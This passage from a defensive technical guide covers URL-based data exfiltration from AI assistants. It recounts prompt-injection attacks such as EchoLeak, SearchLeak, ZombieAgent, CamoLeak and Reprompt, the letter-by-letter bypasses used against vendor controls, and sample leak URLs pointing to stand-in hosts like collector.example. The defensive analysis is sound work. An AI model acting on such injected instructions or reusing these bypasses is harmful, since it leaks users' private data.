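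They also suggest a signed media proxy, a server that fetches an image only if its address carries a valid, unexpired signature from the application. An attacker can't forge the signature. However, the application must not rely on the model's answer to decide which addresses to sign, or it will sign the attacker's address too.

### SearchLeak

A year later, SearchLeak, which Varonis disclosed on 15 June 2026, used a different Microsoft service as the relay. The victim had to click a link, but it led to a genuine microsoft.com page, Copilot's enterprise search. Copilot treated the search text in the link as instructions, searched the victim's mailbox, and put an email's title in an image's URL. The browser requested the image before the output filter ran.

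The policy permitted `*.bing.com`. Bing's search-by-image feature accepts the address of a picture, which Bing's servers then fetch for analysis. The attack supplied an address on the researchers' server with the email's title in the path. The browser sent this address to Bing, and Bing's servers passed the title to the researchers' server when they requested the picture.

The Next Web reports that Microsoft assigned the flaw CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June and rated it critical. The policy that Ravia published in 2025 already listed Bing. Checking after EchoLeak whether each host permitted by that policy fetches URLs for others might have revealed this relay earlier, if the Bing feature worked the same way then. Varonis now recommends such a review.

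In SearchLeak, the email's title travelled as readable words, with underscores for spaces, so a search for Base64 or random characters would have missed it. A search for unlisted hosts in the organisation's proxy log would have missed it too. trackr.live points out that security teams often write log searches that discard every request to an allowlisted host, and that such a search would have hidden both attacks. Requests to known relays need a separate search that decodes the parameters and looks for a second address inside them.

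### A shared storage host

A permitted host can also leak data without fetching anything itself, if strangers can rent space on it. Suppose Acme keeps charts in Amazon's S3 storage service, in a bucket (a customer's named container for files) called `acme-reports`. Acme's assistant needs to display addresses in that bucket, but an injected instruction can make it produce an address in an attacker's bucket on the same host, which the allowlist also permits.

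```
https://s3.amazonaws.com/acme-reports/q2-chart.png
https://s3.amazonaws.com/stranger-bucket/Dr-Lee-12-June.png
```

The host is the same in both. As on an ordinary web server, the image doesn't have to exist, because a bucket's owner can turn on request logs. An entry for `s3.amazonaws.com` therefore permits requests to any customer's bucket. S3 also accepts addresses with the bucket's name in the host, so Acme has several ways to write the entry:

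| Entry | What it permits |
|---|---|
| `s3.amazonaws.com` | Every customer's bucket |
| `*.s3.amazonaws.com` | Every customer's bucket, in addresses that name the bucket in the host |
| Anything beginning `s3.amazonaws.com/acme-reports` | Acme's bucket, but also `acme-reports-2`, which a stranger could register |
| Anything beginning `s3.amazonaws.com/acme-reports/` | Acme's bucket |
| `acme-reports.s3.amazonaws.com` | Acme's bucket |

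The entry with the final slash works only if the monitor resolves `..` in the path before comparing. Otherwise, `/acme-reports/../stranger-bucket/` matches the entry but leads to `stranger-bucket`.

According to trackr.live, a browser enforcing Content Security Policy ignores the path after a redirect and compares only the scheme, host and port. Suppose Acme's policy permits its bucket by path and also permits a site that forwards visitors anywhere. A redirect from that site to `stranger-bucket` would pass, because the two buckets share a host. The last entry in the table avoids this problem because the bucket's name is part of the host, which the browser still compares.

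Three entries in Microsoft's policy for Copilot named individual storage accounts on shared hosts, such as `cpgeneralstore.blob.core.chinacloudapi.cn`. But another entry, `*.sharepoint.com`, permitted the SharePoint sites of every Microsoft customer, including the attacker's.

### What each entry should record

trackr.live describes the boundary that failed in EchoLeak as drawn "around brand, not behavior". Its proposed entry therefore specifies the path, the permitted operation and the owner of the resource as well as the host. It also states whether the service may receive another URL and fetch it. Acme's list might contain these two entries:

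| Field | Chart storage | Link preview service |
|---|---|---|
| Host | `acme-reports.s3.amazonaws.com` | `preview.acme.example` |
| Path | `/charts/` | `/content` |
| Operation | Load an image | Preview a page |
| Owner of the resource | Acme's reporting team | Acme's web team |
| Fetches URLs given to it? | No | Yes, from the `url` parameter |
| Rule | Permit | Permit only if the address in `url` is also on the list |

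The owner should be whoever controls the bucket, site or account, which may not be the company named in the hostname. Ownership can also change. If Acme deletes its bucket and a stranger registers the same name, the old entry still allows requests to the stranger's bucket, so whoever deletes a resource should also delete its allowlist entry.

A developer can fill in the row about fetching by reusing the random-string test for link previews. If the service itself requests the test address, it is a relay. The result can change when the vendor adds a feature, so the test is worth repeating.

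For a relay, the monitor must check the address it is asked to fetch as strictly as the relay's own address, and the relay has to recheck any redirects it follows. If another company runs the relay, Acme can't control whether it does, so it is safer to leave that path off the allowlist. Other services, such as QuickChart and Mermaid's online renderer, fetch nothing but still receive sensitive data because they draw diagrams from text in the URL. trackr.live treats allowing them as a decision to send the diagram's contents to an outside company, which may be acceptable for some data but not for others.

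### What Microsoft and Google deploy

In a July post on its defences against prompt injection, Microsoft (2025) separates probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails. It says that its deterministic defences include blocking the image-based exfiltration that Rehberger reported, and that it took similar steps against other techniques, including the generation of "certain untrusted links". If neither kind is enough, Microsoft relies on the user's explicit consent. For example, Copilot can draft an email in Outlook, but the user has to approve and send it.

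The post doesn't give the rules for deciding which links are untrusted. Eleven months later, SearchLeak showed how narrow a deterministic guarantee can be, since the browser could reliably block images from unlisted hosts and still load one from Bing. Microsoft tells developers that no single solution is sufficient and that they should combine both kinds of defence.

The security company Checkmarx showed that Microsoft Copilot Chat could leak data through an image without the user clicking anything. It reports that Microsoft didn't commit to a fix because it didn't consider the problem a vulnerability. This seems inconsistent with Microsoft's claim that it protects against whole classes of reported issues. A control in one Copilot product may be missing from another, so customers should test the one they use.

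Google's assistant Gemini has a stricter rule for images. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) states that a sanitizer identifies external image addresses and doesn't render them, so EchoLeak's image-based exfiltration doesn't apply to Gemini. Because no outside image hosts are permitted, an attacker can't look among them for one that would relay data. However, users also can't see legitimate outside images in answers.

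For links, Google uses detection based on Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous sites, and replaces suspicious addresses with "suspicious link removed". This is closer to a blocklist than an allowlist. An attacker's newly registered domain may not have a bad reputation yet, so this control is probably weaker against a targeted leak than against known malicious sites.

By April 2026, Google was managing its URL sanitization rules through a central policy engine, which also controlled other deterministic defences such as user confirmation and limits on which tools the model can use in sequence (Gavish, 2026, *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*). Staff can respond to a new attack by changing the configuration, such as by adding a text pattern that removes matching output, without waiting to retrain a model. The main advantage of such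 a pattern is speed, since one written for a particular attack may miss the next variation. Gavish describes simulated attacks with and without each defence but gives no results for URL sanitization.

*The Trifecta*, an outside examination of Gemini by the security company Tenable, reports that Gemini filtered or restricted image Markdown and sent links through a google.com address. The researchers then looked for a way to send data out through Gemini's tools. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes how an injected instruction made the browsing tool open an address containing the user's saved information and location. The tool didn't sufficiently check the destination, and the controls on images and Markdown didn't apply to it. Google has since fixed the flaw.

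## Checking whether the exact URL was already known

EchoLeak and SearchLeak got past Microsoft's allowlist because the browser contacted a permitted host, but the complete URLs were new. Before the attack, nobody had published a Bing image search link containing the title of the victim's email.

An exact-URL check tests for this. It asks whether a source independent of the model's private context, such as a record of the public web, already contained the complete URL. If the URL existed before the conversation, the model can't have written the conversation's data into it. If the model has just composed the URL, it may have. The length and appearance of the URL make no difference:

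| Address | Public before the conversation? | What another check might conclude |
|---|---|---|
| `https://collector.example/lee` | No | Short and ordinary, so harmless |
| `https://photos.example/9f8e2c71b04d6a35/ridge.jpg` | Yes | Random-looking, so suspicious |
| `https://trails.example/go?to=https%3A%2F%2Fcollector.example%2FDr-Lee` | No | On a permitted host, so harmless |

### OpenAI's index

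OpenAI described its version of this check in January 2026. A crawler, a program that discovers pages by following links, records public URLs without access to anyone's conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT retrieves a URL automatically, OpenAI's software checks whether the record contains that exact URL. If it does, ChatGPT loads the page or image. Otherwise, the software either tells ChatGPT to try a different website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation. The warning shows the URL and lets the user copy it or open it anyway.

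OpenAI published a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, alongside the post. In his account of the paper on Embrace The Red, Rehberger says that, as he understands it, ChatGPT also treats any URL the user types as safe for the rest of the session. This is reasonable for a single address, but if a user pastes a whole email into the chat, the exception might cover every link in it, including links the user never looked at.

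The record of known URLs has to be independent of the model's requests. A team that builds its own check can't rely on its web proxy history for this, because that history includes URLs the model wrote. After a malicious request succeeded once, the check would treat an identical request as known.

The warning is probably the weakest part of the design, because it relies on the user to refuse. Willison describes a 2026 Anthropic study in which 1,053 paid testers were each shown one permission prompt for a clearly dangerous command while using a coding agent, and only 13.6% refused it. Anthropic was using the study to argue for an automatic alternative, and approving a command isn't the same as opening a link. Still, the figure suggests that sending the agent to another site is much safer than asking the user. If the user approves an unmatched URL, the monitor should log it for later review.

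### How exact the match has to be

Different URLs can lead to the same page. Newsletters often add tracking parameters to links, so a crawler may have recorded `https://collector.example/map?id=7` while the model requests `https://collector.example/map?id=7&source=june`. If the monitor ignores the extra parameter when comparing the two URLs but still sends the model's version, an injected instruction can make the model write `source=Dr-Lee`, and the name will reach the server.

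It is safer to send the URL exactly as the index stores it. This removes the extra parameter and any other difference that the comparison tolerates, such as capital letters in the path. `/mAp` and `/map` appear differently in a server's log, so an attacker can read a message from which letters are capitals. If the tool drives a full browser, the monitor should also drop any fragment that isn't in the stored URL, since a script on the page could read it.

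Redirects are less of a problem here than with an allowlist. If the first URL was already public, it contains nothing from the conversation that the server could pass on. The server may still learn something from cookies, so the tool should fetch pages without the user's logins.

### Anthropic's context rule

Anthropic's page-fetching tool for developers checks URLs against the conversation rather than a record of the web. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, as it stood in June 2026, states that the tool fetches a URL only if the URL has already appeared in a user's message, in the result of a tool that runs on the developer's side, or in the results of an earlier search or fetch. The tool refuses URLs that Claude composes itself, URLs from Anthropic's code-execution tools, where a program could assemble one, and any URL over 250 characters.

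This rule is much cheaper to run than a crawler, and it lets Claude open a private link that the user has pasted. But it only establishes that the model copied the URL from somewhere, and an attacker can put URLs in the conversation too. The two designs therefore treat the same request differently:

| Request | OpenAI's index | Anthropic's rule, June 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| URL that the model composed | Unmatched | Refused |
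| Unpublished URL from an attacker's email, read with the developer's mail tool | Unmatched | Accepted |
| Attacker's page that the crawler has recorded | Accepted | Accepted if its URL is in the conversation |
| Invoice link in the user's own mail, read with the same tool | Unmatched | Accepted |

Developers should also check what their own tools return. For example, a note-taking tool might confirm each note by repeating its text. If the model saved a URL containing the user's data as a note, the fetch tool would accept that URL under the rule as written, because it had appeared in a tool result.

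Anthropic warns that some risk remains and advises developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive.

### Spelling out data with existing URLs

Both designs still let the model choose among the URLs that pass, and the choice can reveal data. An attacker who wants to know a user's birthday could publish 366 pages, one per date, and induce the model to open the right one. The request would match a public URL exactly. Researchers have demonstrated three attacks that work this way, each against a product whose vendor had restricted which addresses the model could use.

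#### ZombieAgent

After attacks such as ShadowLeak, OpenAI restricted ChatGPT to opening URLs exactly as provided, with nothing added. Radware's *ZombieAgent* got around this restriction with an email containing a ready-made list of URLs, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. The injected instructions told ChatGPT to find sensitive information and open the URLs that spelled it out, so ChatGPT never had to compose a URL. As with ShadowLeak, the requests came from OpenAI's servers.

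Another OpenAI rule stopped ChatGPT from opening an attacker's URLs if they came from its memory of past chats. Radware got around this by planting an instruction in the memory to reread the attacker's email every time the user sent a message. The URLs then came from the email, which the rule didn't cover.

Radware reported the attack on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, the fix stops ChatGPT from opening a link from an email unless the link appears in a well-known public index. The attacker must therefore get the list of URLs into the index before sending the email.

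Leaking data through URLs that are already known may not be difficult. Rehberger says a larger website or blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough for every letter and digit. The attacker only has to tell the model which page stands for which character. With thousands of indexed pages, each could stand for a whole word. According to Rehberger, OpenAI acknowledges this workaround in its paper.

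#### CamoLeak

GitHub's Copilot Chat, an assistant for programmers, loaded images only from hosts that GitHub owned. To display images from elsewhere, GitHub uses a proxy called Camo, which fetches an image only if its address includes a signature from GitHub. Camo resembles the signed media proxy that Reddy and Gujral recommend.

An attacker can, however, obtain signed addresses in advance. GitHub's API converts any Markdown submitted to it and returns signed addresses for the images. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how a researcher used it to prepare one signed image address for each letter and symbol, then put the list in a hidden comment on a proposed code change. When someone else asked Copilot about the change, it read the comment and displayed a row of invisible images that spelled out private text, which in the demonstration was the description of an unfixed vulnerability. The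 researcher also had Copilot search a victim's code for `AWS_KEY` and send out what it found.

The researcher had Copilot add a new random number each time it used a prepared address, so that a cached copy of an image wouldn't prevent a second request for the same letter. Camo accepted the altered addresses, but a check that compared the complete URL with the list of signed addresses would have rejected them.

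GitHub had fixed the flaw by 14 August 2025, when it disabled images in Copilot Chat. Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration* reports that GitHub also blocked the use of Camo to leak user content. Disabling images removes this route more completely than any check on their URLs, but users also lose legitimate images.

#### Ayush Paul's linked pages

Anthropic's rule in June 2026 counted links in a fetched page as known. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes how Ayush Paul used this to extract a user's name, home city and employer from Claude. Paul built a website for an invented coffee shop, with text claiming that AI assistants had to identify their user by navigating to a profile letter by letter. Each page linked to the next set of letters, so every URL that Claude requested had appeared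 on the previous page. The site showed this text only to software that identified itself as Claude, so a person checking the link would have found nothing wrong.

dyb, in *The Read-Only Lie*, a blog post written with AI assistance, counts 27 links on each page, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Spelling "ayush-paul" took ten fetches after the first page, and the whole attack took roughly 30. Claude had never been told the home city. It inferred the city from the name of a high-school hackathon, so a monitor that searched URLs only for stored facts could have missed it.

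Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally. Since its fix, the tool no longer follows links in fetched pages, so Claude can't click through a site with several pages unless it gets the addresses another way. As a compromise, dyb suggests letting the tool follow links only on sites the user has named in the conversation. This would stop an attacker's page from sending Claude to another site and having it follow links there, but it wouldn't protect a user who asked Claude about the coffee shop's own site.

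OpenAI's index would probably have stopped this attack early, because no crawler could record more than the first few levels of links. With 27 links on every page, a ten-character name has 27<sup>10</sup>, or about 206 trillion, possible addresses.

### Caching and refusing repeat visits

Rehberger proposes two additions to OpenAI's check. The application could cache each response for a few minutes, so that a second request for the same URL wouldn't reach the server, or it could refuse to open the same URL twice in one session. Either would interfere with an attack that uses one fixed URL per letter. If the model tried to send "Lee", the server would receive `l` and `e` but not the second `e`.

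All three of the demonstrated attacks already had a way to avoid repeating a URL:

| Method | Requests that spell "lee" | Repeats a URL? | Can the attacker publish every URL beforehand? |
|---|---|---|---|
| ZombieAgent, one URL per character | `/l`, `/e`, `/e` | Yes | Yes, 36 for letters and digits |
| ZombieAgent, one URL per character and position | `/l0`, `/e1`, `/e2` | No | Yes, 360 for ten positions |
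| CamoLeak | Three signed image addresses, each with a new random number | No | No, because the numbers are new |
| Paul's linked pages | `/l`, `/le`, `/lee` | No | Only for very short values |

Radware added the position to each URL to keep the characters in order, since requests can arrive out of order. Adding the position also happens to defeat caching. If an application used a public index and banned repeat visits, it would stop the other three methods in the table for all but the shortest values, but it would not stop this one. The attacker would need 360 indexed pages instead of 36, which is more work but not a serious obstacle for someone who owns a large website.

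A limit on the number of requests applies to all four methods. The `max_uses` setting in Anthropic's tool caps the fetches in each request to the model, but it has no default value. With a cap of 5, Paul's site would have received the first page request and then `a`, `y`, `u` and `s`. A research agent that needs to open 50 pages can't work under such a cap, and a patient attacker can continue in the next request to the model.

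dyb proposes that the monitor also raise an alert when an agent makes a series of requests to one site and each path is one character longer than the last. Documentation with numbered pages can produce similar addresses, so the alert would also require that each added character come from a fixed alphabet and that the requests arrive faster than the conversation's normal browsing.

The condition about speed may not help much. Tencent's *Why AI Agent’s Memory Becomes Attacker’s Data Goldmine* (2026) describes a local reproduction of Paul's attack that extracted an API key from an agent's memory, using 37 characters instead of 27. The server's log showed a delay of one to two seconds between requests, while the agent worked out the next step. An agent reading ordinary pages might go just as fast. (Tencent had told its test agent to follow instructions on web pages, so the experiment shows what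 the log looks like, not how often a commercial product would comply.)

dyb's pattern also misses ZombieAgent, whose paths stay the same length. Looking for many requests to one unfamiliar host whose URLs differ by only a character or two would cover both attacks, though it would flag numbered pages as well. CamoLeak's signed addresses would need another rule, such as an alert for an answer that contains dozens of images.

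### Evidence that the check works

OpenAI's post reports no test results. *The Framing Gap* (2026) offers indirect evidence from experiments in which text from an untrusted source contained instructions to leak a confidential value. The model leaked the value in up to 100% of trials through OpenAI's API, but in none of the 48 valid trials in ChatGPT. If the trials were independent, the ChatGPT result would still be consistent with a true leak rate of up to about 6%.

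The researchers could not see ChatGPT's internal workings and don't attribute the difference to any particular mechanism. The exact-URL check or another product control might have blocked the leaks, or the model may have ignored the instructions in that setting. Telling these explanations apart would require a record of both the URLs the model tried to open and those that reached the server.

Even a working check protects only the parts of a product that use it. OpenAI's earlier URL check was missing from its macOS and mobile apps, and Rehberger expects that some OpenAI developers may not know about the new one.

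Tools that aren't meant for fetching pages can also send URLs. In September 2025, Willison described an attack on the agent in Notion, a note-taking application. The agent's web search tool accepted URLs as well as search terms, so an injected instruction could make the agent put a list of clients into a URL and search for it. A check on Notion's page-fetching tool wouldn't have applied to that request. Developers should therefore run the exact-URL check in the request-sending code that all tools share, or at least list every tool that accepts a URL.

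### Legitimate URLs that are new

Many ordinary requests fail the test because their addresses didn't exist until someone needed them:

| Request | Example | Why a crawler wouldn't have it |
|---|---|---|
| Search page | `https://trails.example/search?q=flat+walk+near+Leeds` | The model wrote the query for this user |
| API call | `https://weather.example/forecast?lat=53.80&lon=-1.55` | It contains this user's location |
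| Personal link | `https://shop.example/invoice.pdf?token=AF3` | The shop sent it to one customer |
| Recent page | `https://news.example/2026/10/07/trail-closures` | The crawler hasn't visited yet |

In the first two rows, the URL contains information about the user that the user wants the recipient to have. An exact-URL check can't distinguish this from a leak. It is better to give the model a narrow tool for such requests. For a weather lookup, the model supplies only a latitude and longitude, and trusted code checks that both are numbers in the valid range and inserts them into a URL on a fixed host. An injected instruction could still make the model supply false numbers, but they would go to the weather service rather than the attacker.

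Personal links are harder to handle because their hosts vary and their tokens are supposed to be secret. These links sometimes become public by accident. *The Silent Spill* (2026) defines a URL leak as an address that gives the public direct access to a private object, such as an invoice link with an access token in the query. If a crawler has recorded such an address, OpenAI's check would let an agent open it automatically. The request would reveal little to the server that wasn't already public, but a match doesn't prove that a URL is free of private data.

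Neither OpenAI's post nor Rehberger's account of the paper gives the check's false positive rate, which is the share of legitimate URLs that fail to match. The rate will vary greatly between applications, but a team can estimate its own by running the check for a few weeks without blocking anything. Suppose an assistant made 2,000 legitimate requests in that time, of which 300 searches and API calls, 200 personal links and 100 recent pages were not in the index. The false positive rate would be 600 out of 2,000, or 30%. Moving the searches and API calls to narrow tools would leave 300 unmatched requests out of 1,700, or about 18%. With real counts, the same calculation would show a team which kind of request to deal with first.

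A rate of 18% is far too high for a system that interrupts the user each time. It may be tolerable if the agent can usually find the same information at a known address, as a research agent often can. An assistant that processes a user's invoices doesn't have that option, because private documents have no public substitute.

### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI also offers a stricter setting, Lockdown Mode, which limits the outbound network requests that could carry data to an attacker. According to Willison, OpenAI first mentioned it in February 2026. By 5 June, OpenAI was rolling it out to eligible personal accounts, including free ones, and to business accounts that customers manage themselves.

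According to the help text Willison quotes, the mode doesn't keep prompt injections out of what ChatGPT reads, and they could still appear in cached web content, for example. This suggests that ChatGPT reads at least some pages from stored copies in this mode. If ChatGPT reads a copy OpenAI already has, the attacker's server receives no request, so the attacker learns nothing even from a choice among 360 published URLs. However, stored pages may be out of date, and pages nobody has stored are unavailable.

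Willison approves of the mode because its restrictions don't depend on a model's judgement, which an attacker could subvert. He also infers from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a determined attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, says the mode "is not meant for everyone" and recommends it to people whose identity, work or the data they handle puts them at elevated risk.

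## Measuring URL length and total volume

An exact-URL check rejects many legitimate searches and API calls because the model has to write those URLs itself. For these requests, a monitor can estimate how much data the URL could hold by counting its characters. This takes little compute and works however the model encoded the data. But most secrets worth stealing are short, so length is more useful for limiting how much data leaks than for detecting a leak.

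### Which length to measure

The simplest measure is the length of the whole URL, but some ordinary links are already long. Here are a pre-signed link to a file in Amazon's S3 storage and a sign-in redirect, with the random parts abbreviated:

```
https://acme-reports.s3.amazonaws.com/charts/q2.png?X-Amz-Algorithm=AWS4-HMAC-SHA256&X-Amz-Credential=AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE%2F20261007%2Fus-east-1%2Fs3%2Faws4_request&X-Amz-Date=20261007T090000Z&X-Amz-Expires=3600&X-Amz-SignedHeaders=host&X-Amz-Signature=[64 characters]

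https://login.example/authorize?response_type=code&client_id=acme-notes&redirect_uri=https%3A%2F%2Fapp.acme.example%2Fcallback&scope=openid&state=[32 characters]&code_challenge=[43 characters]&code_challenge_method=S256
```

The table compares them with a QuickChart link for a plain chart of four quarterly figures and with three leaks to collector.example. The Base64 summary is as long as the one in the Bing Chat demonstration.

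| Request | Whole URL | Path | Longest parameter value | Beyond the endpoint's usual length |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Leak: calendar entry in a parameter | 68 | 14 | 23 | 43 |
| Leak: calendar entry in a file name | 48 | 23 | None | 23 |
| Leak: Base64 summary in a parameter | 313 | 14 | 268 | 288 |
| Pre-signed S3 link | 318 | 14 | 64 | 0 |
| Sign-in redirect | 264 | 10 | 43 | 0 |
| Chart link | 179 | 6 | 149 | 0 |

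A threshold of 250 characters for the whole URL would flag the S3 link and the sign-in redirect but miss both calendar leaks. Measuring the longest parameter value separates the Base64 summary from the S3 link, but the chart link's longest value is still far longer than the calendar entry's. Measuring only parameters also misses data in the path. According to trackr.live, Mermaid's renderer puts its encoded diagram there, so a monitor that checks only the query can miss even an ordinary long link.

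The last column compares each request with the endpoint's own history. For each host and path, the monitor records URL lengths over a few weeks and sets a high threshold, such as the length that 99% of requests stay below. It then counts only the characters beyond that threshold. If an endpoint has no history, the monitor counts everything after the host. The zeros in the table assume that the application has often made similar requests. This measure is probably the best of the four, but an attacker can send a lot of data without raising the count if the endpoint normally receives long URLs, as a chart service does.

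Percent-encoding also inflates the count. A search for 20 katakana characters takes 180 characters in a URL, so a threshold on raw length would flag Japanese searches far more often than English ones. Counting bytes after decoding reduces the count to 60.

### How long ordinary requests are

In *Web Tap*, Borders and Prakash (2004) measured the requests that about 30 volunteers sent through a proxy over 40 days. They counted the bytes a program could change without making the request look abnormal: the URL after the host, any submitted form or file, and the variable parts of the headers. In the first week, the volunteers contacted about 1,600 servers, and only 11 received a request larger than 3 KB.

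The researchers therefore set the threshold for a single request at 3 KB. Over the full 40 days, it produced 38 alerts from 428,608 requests. About 34% of the alerts were false, mostly because of shopping carts and other large forms. If each alert came from one request, the 13 false alarms would mean a false positive rate of only about 0.003% among legitimate requests.

However, a 3 KB threshold would miss all three leaks in the table; it is more than nine times the length of the S3 link. Borders and Prakash were looking for malicious software that uploads files, and web traffic has changed a great deal since 2004. A team can reuse the method, but it should set its threshold based on its own application's traffic.

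### What fits in 250 characters

Anthropic's page-fetching tool has a much lower limit, 250 characters, and rejects longer URLs with the error `url_too_long`. The documentation doesn't explain the limit. It would block the S3 link and the sign-in redirect above. The S3 link would be too long even with a shorter file name, because its query alone is 266 characters. Developers whose agents open such files need another tool to fetch them.

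Suppose a leak uses the 40-character base `https://collector.example/img/pix.png?n=`. That leaves 210 characters for data:

| How the model writes the data | What 210 characters hold |
|---|---|
| Letters and digits, unencoded | 210 characters |
| Any data, in Base64url without padding | 157 bytes |
| Katakana, percent-encoded | 23 characters |
| Katakana, in Base64url | 52 characters |

The 52 complete groups of four characters hold three bytes each, and the last two characters hold one byte, for a total of 157 bytes.

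A six-digit login code, a 16-digit card number and a 20-character password all fit easily within the limit. The email title in the published SearchLeak example, `Your_Security_Code_847291`, is 25 characters long. The limit would block the 313-character URL with the Base64 summary. But if the model wrote the same 200 characters as plain words, with underscores for spaces and no punctuation, the URL would be only 245 characters long.

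Sending a 10,000-byte document in Base64 would take 64 requests, so the limit slows down a large leak, but it can't detect a small one. Lowering the limit to 100 characters would block more legitimate pages and still leave 60 characters for data, enough for the code, the card number or the password. Malware might have to upload a whole mailbox for its owner to search, but an attacker can use an injected instruction to have a language model find the one password in the mailbox and send only that.

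### Reprompt and split exfiltration

Split exfiltration means sending a secret in small pieces over several requests. An attacker can use it to keep every request below a length limit.

The Reprompt attack (CVE-2026-24307) shows how a leak can proceed in stages. Varonis, the company that disclosed SearchLeak, demonstrated it against Copilot Personal, Microsoft's assistant for consumers. According to trackr.live's account, it worked like this:

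1. The user clicked a link whose `q` parameter filled in Copilot's prompt.
2. Copilot's leak check applied only to its first outbound web request, so the prompt told Copilot to make the request twice. The second one got through.
3. The attacker's server replied with further instructions that depended on what it had just received. In successive requests, Copilot sent the time, the user's location, profile data and content from earlier conversations.

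Varonis says the attack didn't affect the enterprise version, Microsoft 365 Copilot.

Checking every request would have closed the gap in step 2, but not necessarily the one in step 3. The later instructions came from the server, so someone who inspected only the original link couldn't have known what Copilot would send. Each reply was short compared with a whole conversation. According to trackr.live, an attacker could adapt the method to keep every request below any fixed length threshold.

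### Adding up a session

To catch data sent in pieces, the monitor has to keep running totals:

1. Group the requests by session and registered domain. On a shared host such as S3, group them by bucket instead.
2. For each request, count the characters beyond the endpoint's usual length.
3. Add them to the group's total before sending the request, and block or flag the request if the total exceeds the threshold.
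4. Keep a second total for each user and day, because a leak can continue in the next conversation.
5. Keep a third total for all unlisted domains together, because an attacker can own several.

Suppose an attacker tries to send out the 10,000-byte document and the threshold for the total is 1,000 characters. Each full request has 225 characters after the host, of which 210 are data. The total reaches 900 after four requests, and the monitor stops the fifth. By then, 628 bytes have left, or about 6% of the document. If the monitor didn't track the total, it would allow all 64 requests, because each is under the 250-character limit.

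Borders and Prakash tested daily totals for each user and site. Lower thresholds produced more alerts, and more of those alerts were false:

| Daily threshold per site | Alerts in 40 days | Share that were false |
|---|---|---|
| 20 KB | 106 | 32% |
| 40 KB | 39 | 15% |
| 60 KB | 18 | 0% |
| 80 KB | 12 | 0% |

With a 20 KB threshold, the 30 volunteers' traffic triggered just under one false alarm a day. At the same rate per person, an organisation of 3,000 people would get about 85 a day. The researchers also counted an alert as correct if it came from an advertising server, a file upload or a program other than a browser. A team looking only for stolen secrets would consider many of those alerts false.

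Even the lowest threshold, 20 KB, is enough data for about a thousand 20-character passwords. The researchers also used Hopster, a program that hides other traffic inside web requests, to carry chat messages. It took three hours to trigger that threshold.

Web Tap's regularity filter caught Hopster sooner, after 80 minutes. The filter divides the day into five-minute intervals and looks for sites that a computer contacts in an unusually large number of intervals. This works for malware that stays on a computer and keeps contacting the attacker. The filter would probably miss an agent that leaks data in a single conversation. At two seconds per request, the 64 requests needed to leak the 10,000-byte document would take about two minutes and fall within one or two intervals.

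### How much a choice among fixed URLs reveals

A character count gives a poor estimate when the model chooses from a fixed list of URLs, as in ZombieAgent, because its choice of URL encodes the data. If N URLs are equally available, each request can carry log<sub>2</sub> N bits. With 36 URLs, that is 5.17 bits per request, and with 1,000 it is 9.97.

The number of requests needed is the size of the secret in bits divided by the bits per request, rounded up. A random code of 20 letters and digits, ignoring capitals, holds 20 × 5.17 = 103.4 bits. The table compares this code with other short secrets:

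| Secret | Size in bits | Requests with 36 URLs | Requests with 1,000 URLs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Birthday, without the year | 8.5 | 2 | 1 |
| Six-digit login code | 19.9 | 4 | 2 |
| 20 letters and digits, ignoring capitals | 103.4 | 20 | 11 |
| 20 letters and digits, with capitals | 119.1 | 24 | 12 |

These numbers apply only if the attacker can recover the order of the requests, no cache suppresses a repeated request, and the model can turn the secret into the right sequence of URLs. Using one URL per character is easy. Treating the whole secret as a large number and rewriting it in base 1,000 is harder, and a model without a tool for running code may make mistakes. An attacker who wants reliable results might use the simpler method even though it takes more requests.

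Web Tap partly accounts for attacks that use many tiny requests by adding two bytes to the count for every request. An AI monitor could add more, but choosing the amount is difficult. Suppose it adds 50 characters per request and has a threshold of 1,000. If an attacker spells out a 20-character code with paths such as `/l`, each request adds 52 to the count. The monitor would stop the twentieth request, but 19 characters would already have leaked, and the attacker could try all 36 possibilities for the last one. An attacker who chose each request from a set of 1,000 URLs could leak the whole code in 11 requests without triggering an alert, while an ordinary gallery of 60 photos would add at least 3,000 to the count, three times the threshold.

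### Counting only what the model adds

A total also counts a copied link the same as one the model wrote itself. If the model copies the 318-character S3 link from a page it has just read, the request reveals little more than which link the model chose.

*Towards Quantification of Network-Based Information Leaks via HTTP* (Borders and Prakash, 2008) proposed measuring only the information that the user's computer adds. The software collected the links on every page the browser received. If the browser requested one of n links on a page, the software counted log<sub>2</sub> n bits. If a URL wasn't among the links, the software counted the whole URL or, for custom programs, how much it differed from recent requests.

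The patent application *Method, system and computer program product for comparing or measuring information content* (Borders, 2009) describes a more precise version. Borders and Prakash published this work as *Quantifying Information Leaks in Outbound Web Traffic* (2009). The newer software also runs the scripts on each page to find the links they create. If no link matches a request exactly, the software takes a close match and counts the changes needed to turn one URL into the other.

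Suppose the agent reads a page with 64 links and requests one of them. Choosing among 64 links takes 6 bits, and the software adds 2 bits to identify the group of links, for a total of 1 byte. If the model appends `?note=Dr%20Lee%2C%2012%20June` to the link, the 29 added characters bring the cost to about 30 bytes. The length of the original link makes no difference. (The software also adds a small amount for the timing of each request.)

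To test the method, Borders collected 507,505 requests from 10 users over 30 days:

| How the software counted | Average bytes per request |
|---|---|
| Everything in the request | 980 |
| Web Tap's earlier method | 243 |
| New data after gzip compression | 132 |
| Only information added by the client | 15.8 |

Individual requests varied widely around the average. Those that exactly matched a known link usually counted as a few bytes, while many others counted as a few hundred. Some of the larger ones contained random numbers or the computer's time, which websites add to URLs to prevent caching. Running the scripts made the counts much lower. In a 30-minute web-mail session, the count fell from 73.3 bytes per request with the 2008 method to 7.8 with the 2009 method.

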